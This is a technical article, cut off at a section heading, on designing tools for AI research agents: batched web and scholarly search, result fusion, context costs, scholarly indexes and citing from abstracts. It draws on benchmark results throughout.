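# Tool design for AI research agents: web search, scholarly search, page reading and code execution

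## Research agents and their tools

A research agent is a language model that investigates a question using outside programs, called tools. It requests a web search, reads the results, requests a page or a calculation, and continues until it can write an answer. *Deep Research Agents*, a survey by Huang, Chen and colleagues (2025), contrasts such agents with the older method of retrieval-augmented generation, in which a fixed procedure typically fetches some documents and the model writes from them. A research agent chooses what to look for next based on what it has already found.

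A language model on its own would struggle to answer a question such as which of five countries had the largest rise in heat-pump sales per head from 2021 to 2024, and whether published studies credit subsidies for it. Its knowledge is stored in its parameters, the numbers that training adjusts, so it doesn't include anything published after training stopped. *WideSearch* (Wong, Wang et al., 2025) points out that a finite set of parameters cannot hold everything, that retraining costs too much to keep a model up to date with the news, and that models struggle with rare or specialised facts. Heat-pump sales in a mid-sized country are one such fact. The model also cannot open the statistics office's page, even if it has the address. Models have become very strong at mathematics, but a model that does arithmetic in running text still predicts each digit, and nothing in that process checks the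 result, as running a program would.

*ReAct* (Yao, Zhao and colleagues, 2022) tested PaLM-540B, a Google model of the time, on questions that require facts from two or more Wikipedia passages. The model either reasoned in text alone or could also consult Wikipedia. The researchers then reviewed 200 of the attempts by hand. Invented facts or reasoning accounted for 56% of the failures when the model reasoned alone, and for none when it could look things up. With Wikipedia, however, 23% of the failures came from searches that returned nothing useful, and 47% came from reasoning errors, compared with 16% without it. Sometimes the model kept repeating the same thought and search. Overall accuracy was slightly lower with Wikipedia, at 27.4% against 29.4%. These figures are dated, since they come from a 2022 model with a deliberately weak search tool, but they show that a tool can remove one source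 of error and introduce others.

### How a tool call works

A language model produces text, so it calls a tool by writing a structured request with the tool's name and arguments, which surrounding software carries out. The developer first describes each tool in the model's instructions. *Tongyi DeepResearch Technical Report* (Tongyi DeepResearch Team, 2025) prints the full instructions for an agent from the Chinese company Alibaba. The description of the search tool is two short sentences stating that it runs Google searches, returns the top results and accepts several queries. A formal definition of the tool's one argument, a list of at least one query, follows.

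To use the tool, the model writes a short block in JSON, a common notation for structured data. For the heat-pump question the block might look like this:

`{"name": "search", "arguments": {"query": ["heat pump sales 2021 by country", "heat pump sales 2024 by country"]}}`

Markers around the block show the software where the request begins and ends. The software reads the tool's name, passes the queries to the search engine, waits for the results, and adds them to the model's input. This returned text is called the observation. The model then continues writing. A turn is one cycle in which the model writes, calls one or more tools and receives the observations.

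A research agent's model reaches the web only through a layer of software. In Alibaba's Tongyi DeepResearch, this layer limits the rate of requests, stores results for reuse, retries calls that time out and switches to a backup search service when the first one fails. The Tongyi DeepResearch Team built it because unreliable tools had threatened to spoil the agent's training. When the agent gave a wrong answer, nobody could tell whether it had made a poor decision or a search service had gone down.

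### The loop, and why it fills up

The whole procedure has a compact formal description. Write τ for a thought (the model's reasoning in text), a for an action and o for an observation. The history before turn t, which follows the question, is

Hₜ₋₁ = (τ₀, a₀, o₀, τ₁, a₁, o₁, …, τₜ₋₁, aₜ₋₁, oₜ₋₁)

and the model produces its next thought and action according to

τₜ, aₜ ~ π(· | Hₜ₋₁)

where π, the policy, stands for the probabilities that the model assigns to each possible continuation, given that history. The last action is the answer, and no observation follows it. The thoughts come from ReAct. Yao and colleagues treated a thought as a special kind of action, one that changes nothing in the outside world and returns no observation. Its only effect is to lengthen the history, but every later step depends on that history, so a plan the model writes down at turn 2 can still steer it at turn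 9.

In a medical case from *AgentFrontier* (Chen, Qiao and colleagues, 2025), an agent could hardly have written its second set of queries before reading the results of its first. The patient's swollen ankle had got worse on a steroid, although the joint fluid showed no sign of infection. The agent's first call sent three queries to Google Scholar, including "prednisone worsens arthritis no crystals". The results indicated that some infections leave no sign in the joint fluid, so the agent's second call searched specifically for bone infection. The agent found that bone infection can produce exactly these findings and correctly answered chronic osteomyelitis.

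The history keeps growing, but a model can take into account only a limited amount of text at once, called its context window. Developers measure the window in tokens, which are words or pieces of words. If the window holds L tokens and an average observation takes up r of them, the agent can complete at most about L/r turns before the history no longer fits. *AgentFrontier* puts an average page visit at 10,000 tokens in its cost accounts. A window of 128,000 tokens would then hold about a dozen complete pages, and the heat-pump question could easily need more. This is why a page reader that returns only the relevant part is useful.

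A growing context causes problems before it overflows. *IterResearch* (Chen, Qiao and colleagues, 2025), a paper from the same laboratory, describes two. Each observation leaves less space for reasoning, which pushes the agent towards hasty conclusions, and irrelevant pages and early mistakes stay in the context for the rest of the run. The agent also needs more computation, since the work of relating every token to every other grows with the square of the context's length.

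Their remedy is to discard most of the history. At each turn the agent starts from a rebuilt workspace containing the question, a running report that it keeps rewriting, and the latest action with its observation. The workspace therefore stays about the same size however long the run lasts. With room for only 40,000 tokens, the agent could run for up to 2,048 turns, though it used about 80 on average. Accuracy on a set of hard browsing questions rose steeply as the turn limit increased from 2 to 2,048, but the paper gives the final figure as 42.5% in one place and 50.1% in another.

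In a more telling comparison, which used identical training data, the agent with the rebuilt workspace averaged 49.1% over six benchmarks, against 36.5% for an agent that kept its full history and had a larger window of 64,000 tokens. So the larger window did not make up for the clutter. The method's drawback is that the agent loses whatever it leaves out of its report. If it notes a sales figure but not the page the figure came from, it will have to find that page again.

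### From WebGPT to deep research

Agents were already starting each step afresh in 2021. *WebGPT* (Nakano, Hilton and colleagues, 2021) gave OpenAI's GPT-3 a text-only browser and, at every step, showed it only a written summary of the current state. The model could search with Bing, follow links, scroll, find text in a page and quote passages as references, taking up to 100 actions before it wrote an answer from what it had quoted. It had learned these commands from about 6,000 human demonstrations. A year later, Yao and colleagues used only a handful of worked examples in the prompt and three commands (search, look up and finish). *Deep Research* (Zhang, Li and colleagues, 2025) traces the later steps from retrieval-augmented generation, through agents that search repeatedly towards a goal, to "deep research" systems that also plan the work and write a structured report. Among commercial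 products, Huang and colleagues date Google's Gemini Deep Research to December 2024, the versions from OpenAI, Perplexity and Grok to February 2025, and Kimi-Researcher to June 2025.

### The tools of Tongyi DeepResearch

Most of those products are closed, and outsiders cannot inspect their tools. Tongyi DeepResearch, whose technical report dates from October 2025, is a useful specimen because its developers published the model, the instructions and the tool definitions. Stronger agents have followed it since. It has five tools:

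| Tool | What the model supplies | What comes back |
|---|---|---|
| `search` | One or more queries, which run at the same time | For each query, the top ten Google results, each with a title, a snippet (a short extract) and an address |
| `google_scholar` | One or more queries | Articles, papers and citations from Google Scholar, along with ordinary Google results |
| `visit` | One or more page addresses and a goal | A summary with only the information that serves the goal |
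| `PythonInterpreter` | Python code | Whatever the code prints |
| `parse_file` | The names of files that the user has uploaded | An answer based on the files' text, including transcripts of audio and video |

Inside the `visit` tool, a second model, the extractor, reads the page and returns what it selects as relevant, so the research agent never receives the page itself. The report is inconsistent about the extractor's goal. The printed definition takes a single goal for a whole list of pages, while an appendix describes a separate goal for each page. Under the printed definition, an agent that opened a table of sales figures and a journal article in one call would have to use the same goal for both.

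The Python tool's JSON arguments stay empty and the code follows separately between markers, presumably because quotation marks and line breaks in code are easy to get wrong inside JSON. The code runs in a sandbox, an isolated environment that limits what it can reach. The instructions also warn the model to print any result it needs, since it can't see results that aren't printed.

The Tongyi DeepResearch Team evaluated its agent with a limit of 128 tool calls per task and a context of 128,000 tokens. One call can carry several queries, so the agent could run more than 128 searches. The context limit is tighter, because an agent that kept its full history and made all 128 calls would have about 1,000 tokens per call, including its own thoughts. Ten search results with snippets could take up much of that. The developers acknowledge that this context is too short for the most complex tasks.

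*IterResearch* and *AgentFrontier* describe nearly the same set without the file parser. The differences are small. For example, AgentFrontier's code tool returns error messages as well as printed output. But all three systems come from Alibaba's Tongyi Lab, so their agreement doesn't prove that developers elsewhere settled on the same design. Huang and colleagues provide better evidence. They find search and code execution among the core components of agents from many groups, though some of those agents use a full browser instead of a page reader like Tongyi's.

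For the heat-pump question, the work might divide up like this:

1. `search` takes a batch of queries on sales and population in the five countries, and returns candidate pages.
2. `visit` opens the best candidates, with the goal of finding units sold in 2021 and 2024.
3. `PythonInterpreter` divides sales by population, subtracts the 2021 figure from the 2024 figure and ranks the countries.
4. `google_scholar` looks for studies of subsidies and heat-pump purchases.
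5. `visit` opens those studies with a new goal: whether the researchers credit subsidies, and on what evidence.

A real run would be less tidy. One country's data might end at 2023, so the agent would have to return to step 1, or one national count might include reversible air conditioners while another excludes them. "Largest rise" could also mean extra units per thousand people or percentage growth, and a different country might come first on each measure. The tools can't settle which meaning is intended, so the model has to choose one and state it in the answer.

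### Four benchmarks

Researchers compare agents on benchmarks, shared sets of questions with known answers. Four of them come up repeatedly:

- BrowseComp has 1,266 questions that are hard to solve but have short, easily checked answers, as *Improving and Evaluating Open Deep Research Agents* (2025) describes it, and agents look for those answers on the live web.
- BrowseComp-Plus, which *BrowseComp-Plus* (2025) introduced, replaces the live web with a fixed collection so that *CAFE* (2026) and other later work can compare agents under the same conditions; *CORE* (2026) gives its size as 830 questions and 100,195 documents, misleading near-matches among them.
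- WideSearch, from Wong and colleagues, has 200 questions, half in English and half in Chinese, that each require a complete table; a single wrong or missing entry fails the task, and the best system in 2025 succeeded about 5% of the time.
- Humanity's Last Exam has 2,500 very difficult questions by experts in many academic fields, of which both *AgentFrontier* and the Tongyi DeepResearch Team use the 2,154 that consist of text alone.

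## Searching the web with several queries at once

In batch search, an agent sends several queries in one tool call. For the heat-pump question, an agent with Tongyi DeepResearch's `search` tool could send a list of five queries, one for each country. The software passes all five to the search engine at the same time and returns fifty results, ten per query. The model reads all fifty before it writes anything else.

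*DEEPPLANNER* (Fan, Yao and colleagues, 2025) describes a search tool of almost the same form. The software also stores each query with its results, so when the agent later opens one of the pages, the page reader has the query that led there.

Some developers prefer a search tool that accepts a single query rather than a list. Seng (2026) describes one in *Simple Abstractions, Dense Payloads*, an engineering article from the search company You.com, and argues that every extra parameter gives the model another decision it could get wrong on every call. An agent with such a tool can still search in parallel if its model can write several tool calls in one turn, as many commercial models can. Separate calls achieve nearly the same result as a list of queries, but they use up a limit on tool calls faster. Most experiments on parallel search have used separate calls. Some agents instead write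 a program that runs the searches, about 12 per call in *BrowseMaster* (2025).

### Separate needs and rewordings

The five country queries are for five different facts, so the agent needs five separate lists of results, each labeled with its query. But an agent might also send "heat pump sales Poland 2024" together with "Polish heat pump market units sold 2024", which are two wordings of the same question. A page that ranks well for both is probably a good one, so the software can merge the lists, drop the duplicates and keep only the best few results, which saves tokens.

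A common way to merge them is reciprocal rank fusion, which comes from Cormack, Clarke and Büttcher (2009), in *Reciprocal Rank Fusion outperforms Condorcet and individual Rank Learning Methods*. Each page d gets a score

score(d) = Σᵢ 1 / (k + rankᵢ(d))

where rankᵢ(d) is the page's place in list i and k is a constant, 60 in the original paper. If a page is missing from a list, that list adds nothing to its score, as *Hindsight is 20/20* (2025), a paper on memory for agents, spells out. The software then sorts the pages by score. Suppose the two Polish queries return three pages each:

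| Page | Place in list 1 | Place in list 2 | Score with k = 60 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Statistics office table | 3 | 1 | 1/63 + 1/61 = 0.0323 |
| Industry report | 2 | 3 | 1/62 + 1/63 = 0.0320 |
| News article | 1 | absent | 1/61 = 0.0164 |
| Blog post | absent | 2 | 1/62 = 0.0161 |

The news article came first in list 1 but finishes third, because list 2 didn't contain it.

With lists this short, the formula ranks pages mainly by how many lists they appear in. A page in two ten-result lists scores at least 2/70, or 0.0286, so it always ranks above a page in only one list, which can score at most 1/61, or 0.0164. That suits rewordings of the same query, but it would give poor results for the five countries. A general article on European heat pumps in tenth place for both Poland and Italy would rank above the best page on each country, and a merged list of ten would have room for only about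 two pages per country.

Cormack and colleagues designed the formula for rankings of a whole document collection, where k limits how much a page gains from being first in a single ranking. In a pilot test, they merged the rankings from 30 configurations of one search system. The merged ranking scored 0.2145 on mean average precision, a standard measure of ranking quality that runs from 0 to 1, against 0.2016 for the best single configuration. Every value of k they tried from 0 to 500 scored between 0.207 and 0.215, so the choice hardly mattered. *Data Fusion of Synthetic Query Variants With Generative Large Language Models* (2024) applied the same formula, with the same k, to queries reworded by a language model.

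Researchers disagree about whether any method is better than reciprocal rank fusion. *An Analysis of Fusion Functions for Hybrid Retrieval* (2022) found that a weighted sum of the search systems' own relevance scores, with the weight tuned on sample data, ranked documents better on every dataset. In *BIT.UA at BioASQ 14B* (2026), which describes a biomedical question-answering system, reciprocal rank fusion consistently beat a weighted sum. The dispute makes no practical difference for an agent that searches Google through a tool like Tongyi's, because the results arrive without scores and the software can only use their order.

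Merging results from more varied queries doesn't always help, either. *R2QRec* (2026) shows this with a small example. Suppose the page the agent needs, t, comes second in two lists. If both lists rank the pages a, t, b, then t finishes second in the merged list. If the lists are more varied, with one ranking the pages a, t, b and the other b, t, a, then t finishes last, because a first and a third place together score slightly more than two second places.

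### Time and tokens

We can roughly estimate what a batch saves on the five country queries. *HierSearch* (2025) estimates 2.30 seconds for a web search and 12.57 milliseconds for each token of reasoning. We also assume that the model writes 200 tokens per turn when it searches one country at a time and 300 tokens in the single turn that searches all five, that each result is 80 tokens long, and that the instructions and question total 3,000 tokens.

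| | Five turns, one query each | One turn, five queries |
|---|---|---|
| Waiting for search results | 11.5 s | 2.3 s |
| Writing thoughts and calls | 12.6 s | 3.8 s |
| Total time | 24.1 s | 6.1 s |
| Tokens of search results | 4,000 | 4,000 |
| Tokens the model reads in total | 33,000 | 10,300 |

The batch is about four times as fast as separate searches, and nearly half of the time saved comes from the agent writing less. But a batch takes as long as its slowest query, so one search that hangs for ten seconds delays the results of the other four.

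Fifty results take up 4,000 tokens whether the queries run one at a time or in a batch, about 3% of a 128,000-token window. Batching saves tokens because the model has to read the entire history each time it continues, and it continues fewer times. In the sequential run, it reads 3,000 tokens before the first query, 4,000 before the second, and so on up to 8,000 after the last results arrive, for a total of 33,000. In the batch, it reads 3,000 and then 7,300, for a total of 10,300.

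In general, if the instructions and question take b tokens and each of n turns adds c more, the model reads

(n + 1)b + c·n(n + 1)/2

tokens in all, so the total eventually grows with the square of the number of turns. Fifty single searches would come to about 1.4 million tokens on these assumptions, and ten batches of five to about 270,000. The bill falls by less than that, because many providers charge a lower price for text that the model has already processed in an earlier call.

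### Queries that have to wait

Some queries depend on the answer to another query. The agent can't look for studies of subsidies in the country with the largest rise until it knows which country that is. It could instead search for subsidy studies on all five countries at the start. Four of those searches would be wasted, but their forty results would add only about 3,200 tokens, and the agent might save a turn. This works because there are only five candidates. If the question asked who founded the company that makes Poland's best-selling heat pump, the agent couldn't write the second query without knowing the company's name.

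*A-MapReduce* (2026) describes a system for filling in large tables from the web. Its search agent pursues independent goals in parallel but tries the fallback steps within each goal one after another, which is a sensible rule for mixed cases.

Telling a model to batch all its searches can add turns with little or no gain in accuracy. *ParallelSearch* (2025) added an instruction to search in parallel to Search-R1, an open search agent. On questions from the HotpotQA benchmark whose steps depend on each other, the share of exactly correct answers stayed at 31%, while the average number of turns rose from 2.3 to 3.3. On a second question set, accuracy went from 21.2% to 21.5% and turns from 2.7 to 3.7.

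### Parallel against sequential search

Zhang, Lin and colleagues (2026) make the cleanest comparison in *CHART*. They trained two copies of a 30-billion-parameter Qwen model on the same data with the same reward, and gave each a budget of about 25 searches per question. One copy could take up to 25 turns with one call in each. The other had five turns with up to five calls in each.

| | Sequential | Parallel |
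|---|---|---|
| Correct answers (150 questions) | 47.3% | 51.3% |
| Turns per question | 10.9 | 2.5 |
| Searches per question | 10.9 | 10.5 |
| Tokens read per question | 67,000 | 26,500 |

The agents' accuracy differed by six questions, and each agent tried every question only once, so the difference could easily be due to chance. The difference in tokens read is much harder to doubt, because the sequential agent read two and a half times as many even though both agents ran about the same number of searches and wrote about the same amount of text. It read more for the reason shown in the formula.

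Lin, Liew and colleagues (2026), in *W&D*, varied the number of calls per turn. Before each turn their software inserted a message telling GPT-5, a 2025 model, how many calls to make, counting page visits as well as searches. These are the percentages of correct answers on the first 100 questions of BrowseComp:

| Most turns allowed | 1 call per turn | 3 calls per turn | 8 calls per turn |
|---|---|---|---|
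| 10 | 44 | 48 | 56 |
| 25 | 55 | 68 | 67 |
| 100 | 66 | 68 | 63 |

With only ten turns, making more calls per turn clearly improved accuracy. This is unsurprising, since the agent with the most calls per turn could make about 80 in total and the one with the fewest about ten. With 100 turns, the accuracy advantage disappeared, but making more calls per turn still saved money and time. Three calls per turn cost $65.70 for the hundred questions instead of $102.50, and the average run took 904 seconds instead of 1,523.

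Lin and colleagues also tried changing the number of calls per turn during a run. Starting with three and dropping to two and then one gave 74% correct answers, while the reverse order gave 63%. It makes sense for an agent to search broadly first and follow up details later, though a hundred questions is a small sample for judging an 11-point gap. Other models gained less. DeepSeek-V3.2 went from 38% to 39% with three calls per turn, and an older Qwen model went from 8% to 11% but needed an average of 52 turns instead of 18.5.

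The researchers read individual runs and saw some ways parallel calls might improve answers. In one run, the agent had to identify a football match from the early 1990s using details about the referee, yellow cards and substitutions. With one call per turn, it put all these details into a single query and got poor results, while with several calls it searched separately for the matches of particular referees at the 1990 and 1994 World Cups and found what it needed. In another example, about women's seats in North African parliaments, the single-call agent accepted a figure of 22.25% from a database, while the parallel agent compared several sources and chose the 24.3% in the United Nations yearbook. These cases were hand-picked, so they suggest explanations but don't show how often each one applies.

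Searching in parallel can also increase wasted work. *Explore Before Committing* (2026) tested an agent that can split its search into several hypotheses and pursue them side by side. Without splitting, it answered 58.3% of a small question set correctly and made 42 tool calls per question. When it split on every question, accuracy rose to 63.3% and calls to 149. Splitting only when the situation seemed to need it did best, at 66.7% with 139 calls, which is still more than three times as many as without splitting. An agent can also do well without much batching. On AgentHop, a test of literature search, the most accurate model rarely batched.

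*Deep Researcher with Sequential Plan Reflection and Candidates Crossover* (2026) argues for working in sequence because parallel branches repeat each other's searches and can't use each other's findings. This objection is fair for systems whose agents work in isolation. It applies less to a batch of queries, because one model writes them all together and reads all the results before its next step.

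An agent trained to batch its queries may do so much less when its instructions change. Zhang and colleagues found that their parallel agent batched on 91% of turns under the instructions it had trained with, 45% under other instructions that still asked for parallel search, and 2% under instructions that didn't mention it. A developer who rewrites an agent's instructions for an unrelated reason could therefore lose the savings from batching without noticing. To prevent this, the researchers kept changing the instructions during training, replacing each set once the model had learned to batch under it. The resulting agent batched on 89% of turns under instructions it had never seen.

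### What a better search engine adds

An agent depends on what the search engine finds, however many queries it sends. *BrowseComp-Plus* measured this on its fixed collection by changing only the retriever, the program that picks documents for a query. One retriever, BM25, scores documents by the words they share with the query. The other, Qwen3-Embedding-8B, turns the query and every document into lists of numbers that represent their meaning, and picks the documents whose numbers are closest to the query's. Each search returned the first 512 tokens of five documents.

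| Model | Accuracy with BM25 | Accuracy with Qwen3 | Searches with BM25 | Searches with Qwen3 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 55.9% | 70.1% | 23.2 | 21.7 |
| o3 | 49.3% | 63.5% | 25.9 | 24.0 |
| Claude Opus 4 | 15.5% | 36.1% | 11.2 | 10.2 |
| GPT-4.1 | 14.6% | 35.4% | 10.4 | 8.7 |

The better retriever added at least 14 points for each of these models and saved one or two searches per question. When the researchers gave GPT-4.1 all the documents with relevant evidence, it answered 93.5% of the questions correctly, so nearly all of its difficulty was in finding the documents.

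Finding more of the evidence doesn't always lead to more correct answers, though. In *Programmatic Search Agents* (2026), three lighter models from 2026 that searched with ordinary queries answered between 33% and 55% of the same questions correctly. Of the three, Qwen3.8-Flash retrieved the most evidence (63%) but gave the fewest correct answers.

Results on the same benchmark show why agents need to break questions up. When the researchers used the whole question as the query, the top five results contained 1.2% of the evidence documents with BM25 and 14.5% with the better retriever. Each question combines several clues, often from different pages, so a single search is unlikely to find them all.

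### Repeated queries

In *A Picture of Agentic Search*, Pezzuti, Frieder and colleagues (2026) recorded the queries that three small open agents, with 3 to 7 billion parameters, wrote for about 200,000 questions, and compared each query with the earlier ones in the same run. The agents tended to alternate between a substantially new wording and an exact copy of an earlier query, apparently returning to the earlier query when the new wording failed. The longest run contained 186 queries, whereas people usually give up after two or three rewordings.

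Exact copies made up only 5% of the agents' queries on one question set, compared with 12% of people's, so the loops were probably concentrated in a minority of runs. Near-copies were much more common. Queries for the same original question overlapped by an average of 35% on one set and 83% on another, measured as shared items divided by all distinct items. Larger models may well loop less, since these three were small even for their time.

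Near-identical queries are especially wasteful in a batch. Five of them return many of the same pages, so the agent may retrieve fifty results but only fifteen different ones. The software can remove repeated addresses before the model reads them, but only after the searches have run. Pezzuti and colleagues suggest that a search service could take advantage of this overlap by reusing stored results for any query similar enough to an earlier one. However, queries with similar wording can need different results. An agent that got the same results for "heat pump sales 2021" and "heat pump sales 2024" would wrongly conclude that sales had not changed.

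### The software around the call

A batch strains the software around the search tool more than a single query does. Five queries sent at once can hit a rate limit like the one in the *Tongyi DeepResearch Technical Report*. If the search service allows two queries per second, the fifth is sent two seconds late, and the batch takes 4.3 seconds instead of 2.3.

If one query times out, the software should retry only that query and keep the results it already has from the others. It shouldn't repeat a request that the service rejected as badly formed, because the request will fail again. A backup search engine covers different pages and ranks them differently, so developers who compare agents need a record of which engine handled each query. Storing results makes repeated queries free and keeps test runs comparable, but stored results won't include news published after they were saved.

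The search tool also needs to report what happened to each query. Suppose four searches succeed and the Polish one fails even after retries. If the tool reports one error for the whole batch, the agent loses forty results. If it returns the forty results without mentioning the failure, the model may conclude that nobody publishes Polish sales figures. A short status line for each query, such as "10 results", "0 results" or "failed after 3 attempts", avoids both problems. Tongyi's search tool returns everything as a single block of text, so each status has to appear in that text to reach the model.

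Even a genuine "0 results" is weak evidence that something doesn't exist. It means one wording found nothing in one search engine, and the query may have had too many conditions, like the one about the football match. One set of instructions in *CHART* tells the model to stop rephrasing after two failed searches in a row and instead break the question down differently, look for a related person or thing, or try another angle.

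Successful searches can also mislead, because a snippet often leaves out what the reader needs to interpret it. For example, "sales rose to 200,000 units" might refer to 2022 or include air conditioners, with the explanation in a heading further up the page. *OpenResearcher* (2026) gives incomplete snippets as a reason for adding tools that open a page and find text in it. In *BrowseComp-Plus*, GPT-4.1's accuracy rose from 35.4% to 43.6% when it could open whole documents, although it opened fewer than two per question. Its search previews were 512 tokens long, much longer than an ordinary snippet, so an agent that relies on Google's snippets probably misses more.

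Some developers accept the risk for speed. The same instructions in *CHART* tell the model to answer as soon as a snippet clearly contains the answer, without searching further to verify it. That is reasonable for an easy question if the snippet is accurate, but a snippet from a malicious page may be misleading. It is a poor rule for the heat-pump question, where one wrong sales figure could change which country comes first. Opening the page to check would take about three seconds, according to the estimate in *HierSearch*.

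## Searching the scholarly literature

The last part of the heat-pump question is whether published studies credit subsidies for the rise in sales. A web search would return any such studies alongside news articles and manufacturers' pages, and a snippet seldom shows who wrote a study or where it appeared. A scholarly search tool returns records of academic papers. In *IterResearch*, for example, Chen and colleagues gave their agent a Google Scholar tool whose results list each paper's authors, venue (journal or conference), citation count and part of its abstract. Some tools also provide the publication year and full reference list.

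An agent can use these details to rule papers out quickly. A paper from 2019 can't explain sales in 2024, and two papers by one team on the same data are weaker evidence than two independent ones. Citation counts are less useful because they measure attention rather than quality and take years to accumulate.

### The main indexes

Behind each tool is an index, or backend. Five are common:

| Backend | What it covers | Full text | Terms |
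|---|---|---|---|
| Google Scholar | All fields, including theses, books and preprints | No, but links to copies on the web | No official interface for programs, so developers pay a service such as SerpAPI or Serper |
| Semantic Scholar | All fields | No, but links to open-access PDFs | Free interface with rate limits |
| OpenAlex | All fields | No, but links to open-access copies | Public-domain data (a CC0 licence), which anyone may redistribute |
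| arXiv | Preprints, mostly in physics, mathematics and computer science | Yes | Free to read; authors choose the licence for reuse |
| PubMed | Medicine and the life sciences | No, but its sister archive PubMed Central has many papers | Free |

No scholarly index is complete. *Distribird* (2026) describes a system that queries Semantic Scholar and OpenAlex in parallel because they cover different sets of papers. *Investigating Document Type, Language, Publication Year, and Author Count Discrepancies* (2025) reports finding 86.5% of 7.6 million articles from Web of Science, a commercial index, in OpenAlex.

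Gaps in coverage vary by journal. *Comparison of OpenAlex and Scopus coverage of German institutions' publications* (2026) found that, for 2020 to 2025, OpenAlex had 91 records from the *Journal of Machine Learning Research*, while the commercial index Scopus had 2,022. For the *Journal of Clinical Oncology*, OpenAlex had far more, 46,814 against 7,600, perhaps because it counts the conference abstracts that the journal prints. An agent that searches only one index could therefore miss most of a journal without any sign of the gap. Abstracts can be missing too. *Beyond coauthorship* (2026), a study of transportation research, had to get many older abstracts from a publisher because OpenAlex had few from before about 2010.

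Full text is harder to get than a record. In *DeepSciVerify* (2026), a search for 412 cited papers found abstracts for 95% and full text for 81%. PubMed Central supplied three quarters of the full texts, and a language model searching the web found the rest. *Affinage* (2026), which describes a system for summarising what genes do, reports that open sources alone yielded full text for only about 46% of the cited papers, with paywalls blocking many of the others.

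Some scholarly search tools also return general web results. Tongyi DeepResearch's `google_scholar` tool adds ordinary Google results, and the one in *IterResearch* falls back on general web search. This widens coverage, but a model that finds a manufacturer's report in the output of a tool called `google_scholar` could easily mistake it for a study. Labelling each result with the index it came from would help, though a Google Scholar label doesn't guarantee peer review.

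The backend may also change between an agent's training and its use. In *DEEPRUBRIC*, Zhu, Wei and colleagues (2026) trained an agent whose scholarly tool searched a local copy of OpenScholar, a collection of papers, by meaning. When they evaluated the agent, a tool with the same name queried Google Scholar through Serper instead. The local copy made training faster, cheaper and more stable because thousands of practice runs didn't depend on an outside service.

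The agent still performed well after the change, scoring 86.0 on a test of scientific question answering, compared with 57.2 for the original model with search. But these scores don't show how much the switch itself hurt performance, because they don't compare the trained agent on both backends. The agent may have learned to write long, descriptive queries that suit a search by meaning but work less well in Google Scholar.

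### Keywords and references

A researcher can also find papers by following the references in a paper. *AgentHop* (Park, Yoon and colleagues, 2026) tests agents on this with 1,011 questions about computer-science papers, each with four possible answers. The agent receives the question, the options and one starting paper, called the seed. The answer lies in one or two other papers, which the seed cites either directly or through one paper in between. On average, 311 papers lie within two links of the seed.

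The agent has seven tools, and most calls cost points:

| Tool | Points | What comes back |
|---|---|---|
| `get_paper_info` | 1 | Title, abstract, year and venue |
| `get_references` | 1 | The papers that a paper cites, with the sentence that cites each one |
| `list_sections` | 1 | Section headings and their lengths |
| `search_papers` | 1 | Up to ten papers that match a keyword query, with abstracts |
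| `read_section` | 5 | The full text of one section |
| `think` | 0 | Nothing new; the model's note stays in the history |
| `submit_answer` | 0 | Nothing; the run ends |

Each run has a limit of 20 turns, 200,000 tokens and 30 points. Reading uses many points by design, so an agent that reads four sections has ten points left for finding them. A run that hits a limit before the agent answers counts as wrong. The best of 19 models, Gemini-3 Pro, answered 89.1% of the questions correctly, though stronger models have come out since.

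Park and colleagues then took tools away from three of the models:

| Model | No tools | All tools except keyword search | All tools |
|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-chat | 18.3% | 53.3% | 56.4% |
| Gemma-4-31B | 31.7% | 54.8% | 64.8% |
| GPT-5.3 codex | 48.6% | 79.3% | 82.5% |

DeepSeek-chat's 18.3% is worse than the 25% that guessing would give, probably because the wrong options look plausible to a model that hasn't read the papers.

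Keyword search added only 3 to 10 points, and Park and colleagues call it dispensable. Within the benchmark, their case is stronger than the table shows, because the table uses only the first of three runs with the full set of tools, and that run was the best for every model. Averaging the three runs gives 55.3%, 60.5% and 81.8%, which would reduce the gain from keyword search to between 2 and 6 points.

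The conclusion doesn't apply to open questions, though. Every AgentHop run starts from a seed that is at most two links from the answer, while someone who asks about heat pumps supplies no seed, so the agent has to find one first. Keyword search also has little chance to help in this benchmark. The tool searches only the papers around the seed, most of which the agent could reach through reference lists anyway. And GPT-5.4, which wrote the questions, was told not to use the target paper's title or the names of its methods, which are the words that keyword search matches best.

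The experiment also does not show that following references produced the gain of 23 to 35 points over no tools. The agents without keyword search could both follow references and read the papers, and either ability might account for much of the gain. A run with keyword search and reading but no reference lists would help separate their effects.

Agents find far fewer of the right papers when they start from a topic alone. In *TaxoBench* (2026), the best of seven deep-research agents found 21% of the papers that experts had cited on a topic. Three newer agents reached at most 25%, mainly by listing more papers. Some of the agents' other papers may also have been relevant, since an expert's list is one possible selection. *Self-prompting and cross-model consensus enable reproducible data extraction from scientific literature* (2026) tested agents on the narrower task of finding papers from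 before 2005 that measured how a heart-muscle protein, troponin C, binds calcium. The best agent still missed about half of the experts' references.

References also lead only to older work. The reference list of a 2023 paper on heat-pump subsidies can't include a 2025 study that contradicts it. Google Scholar, Semantic Scholar and OpenAlex solve this by listing the papers that cite a given paper, but AgentHop has no such tool. For an open question, it makes sense to find a few good papers by keyword, then look through the papers they cite and the papers that cite them.

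### Citing papers from their abstracts

Agents often cite sources they haven't opened. *Quantifying Claim Smoothing by LLM Research Agents* (Singha Roy, Wadhwa and Durrett, 2026) found that OpenAI's GPT Luna 5.6 opened only 19% of the pages it cited. *Retrieved but Not Read* (2026) gave models the same search results and found that they answered without opening any page between 2.6% and 76% of the time, depending on the model. Both studies looked at general web search. Agents are probably more likely to skip opening academic papers, because an abstract reads like a complete summary.

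Abstracts often leave out details that are in the full text. *When AI Meets Science* (2026) looked for uses of AI methods in scientific papers and found them in 2.1% of papers when it used the abstracts, but in 7.6% when it used the full texts. Missing details also make papers harder to find. In *Benchmarking Literature Retrieval for a Model Organism* (2026), a search for the source of one claim about a slime mould ranked the right paper 54th when the index contained only abstracts. The paper's abstract didn't mention the relevant evidence. Adding passages from full texts to the index moved the paper to first place.

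Reading the full text isn't always worth the extra tokens. *Affinage* gave its system whole papers where it could get them, and the system extracted 16% more findings but used about 15 times as many tokens in the reading stage. A model that compared the resulting gene summaries chose the full-text version 20 times and the abstract-only version 24 times, with 33 ties. Abstracts may therefore be enough for a general summary, but relying on them is much riskier when an agent needs a specific number or has to tell whether a study credits subsidies for a result or only mentions them.

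*ReviewPilot* (2026) describes a system for extracting data from studies, with a sensible rule for papers without full text. The model may fill in a field only if the abstract states or necessarily implies the value, and it must quote the supporting sentence. It leaves the other fields blank and can then search the web for the missing values, but only on pages about the same paper, such as its entry in a trial registry. A research agent could follow the same rule, with each citation marked "abstract only" or "full text". The surrounding software can add these marks itself, using its log of the papers the agent opened.

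### Counting one study twice

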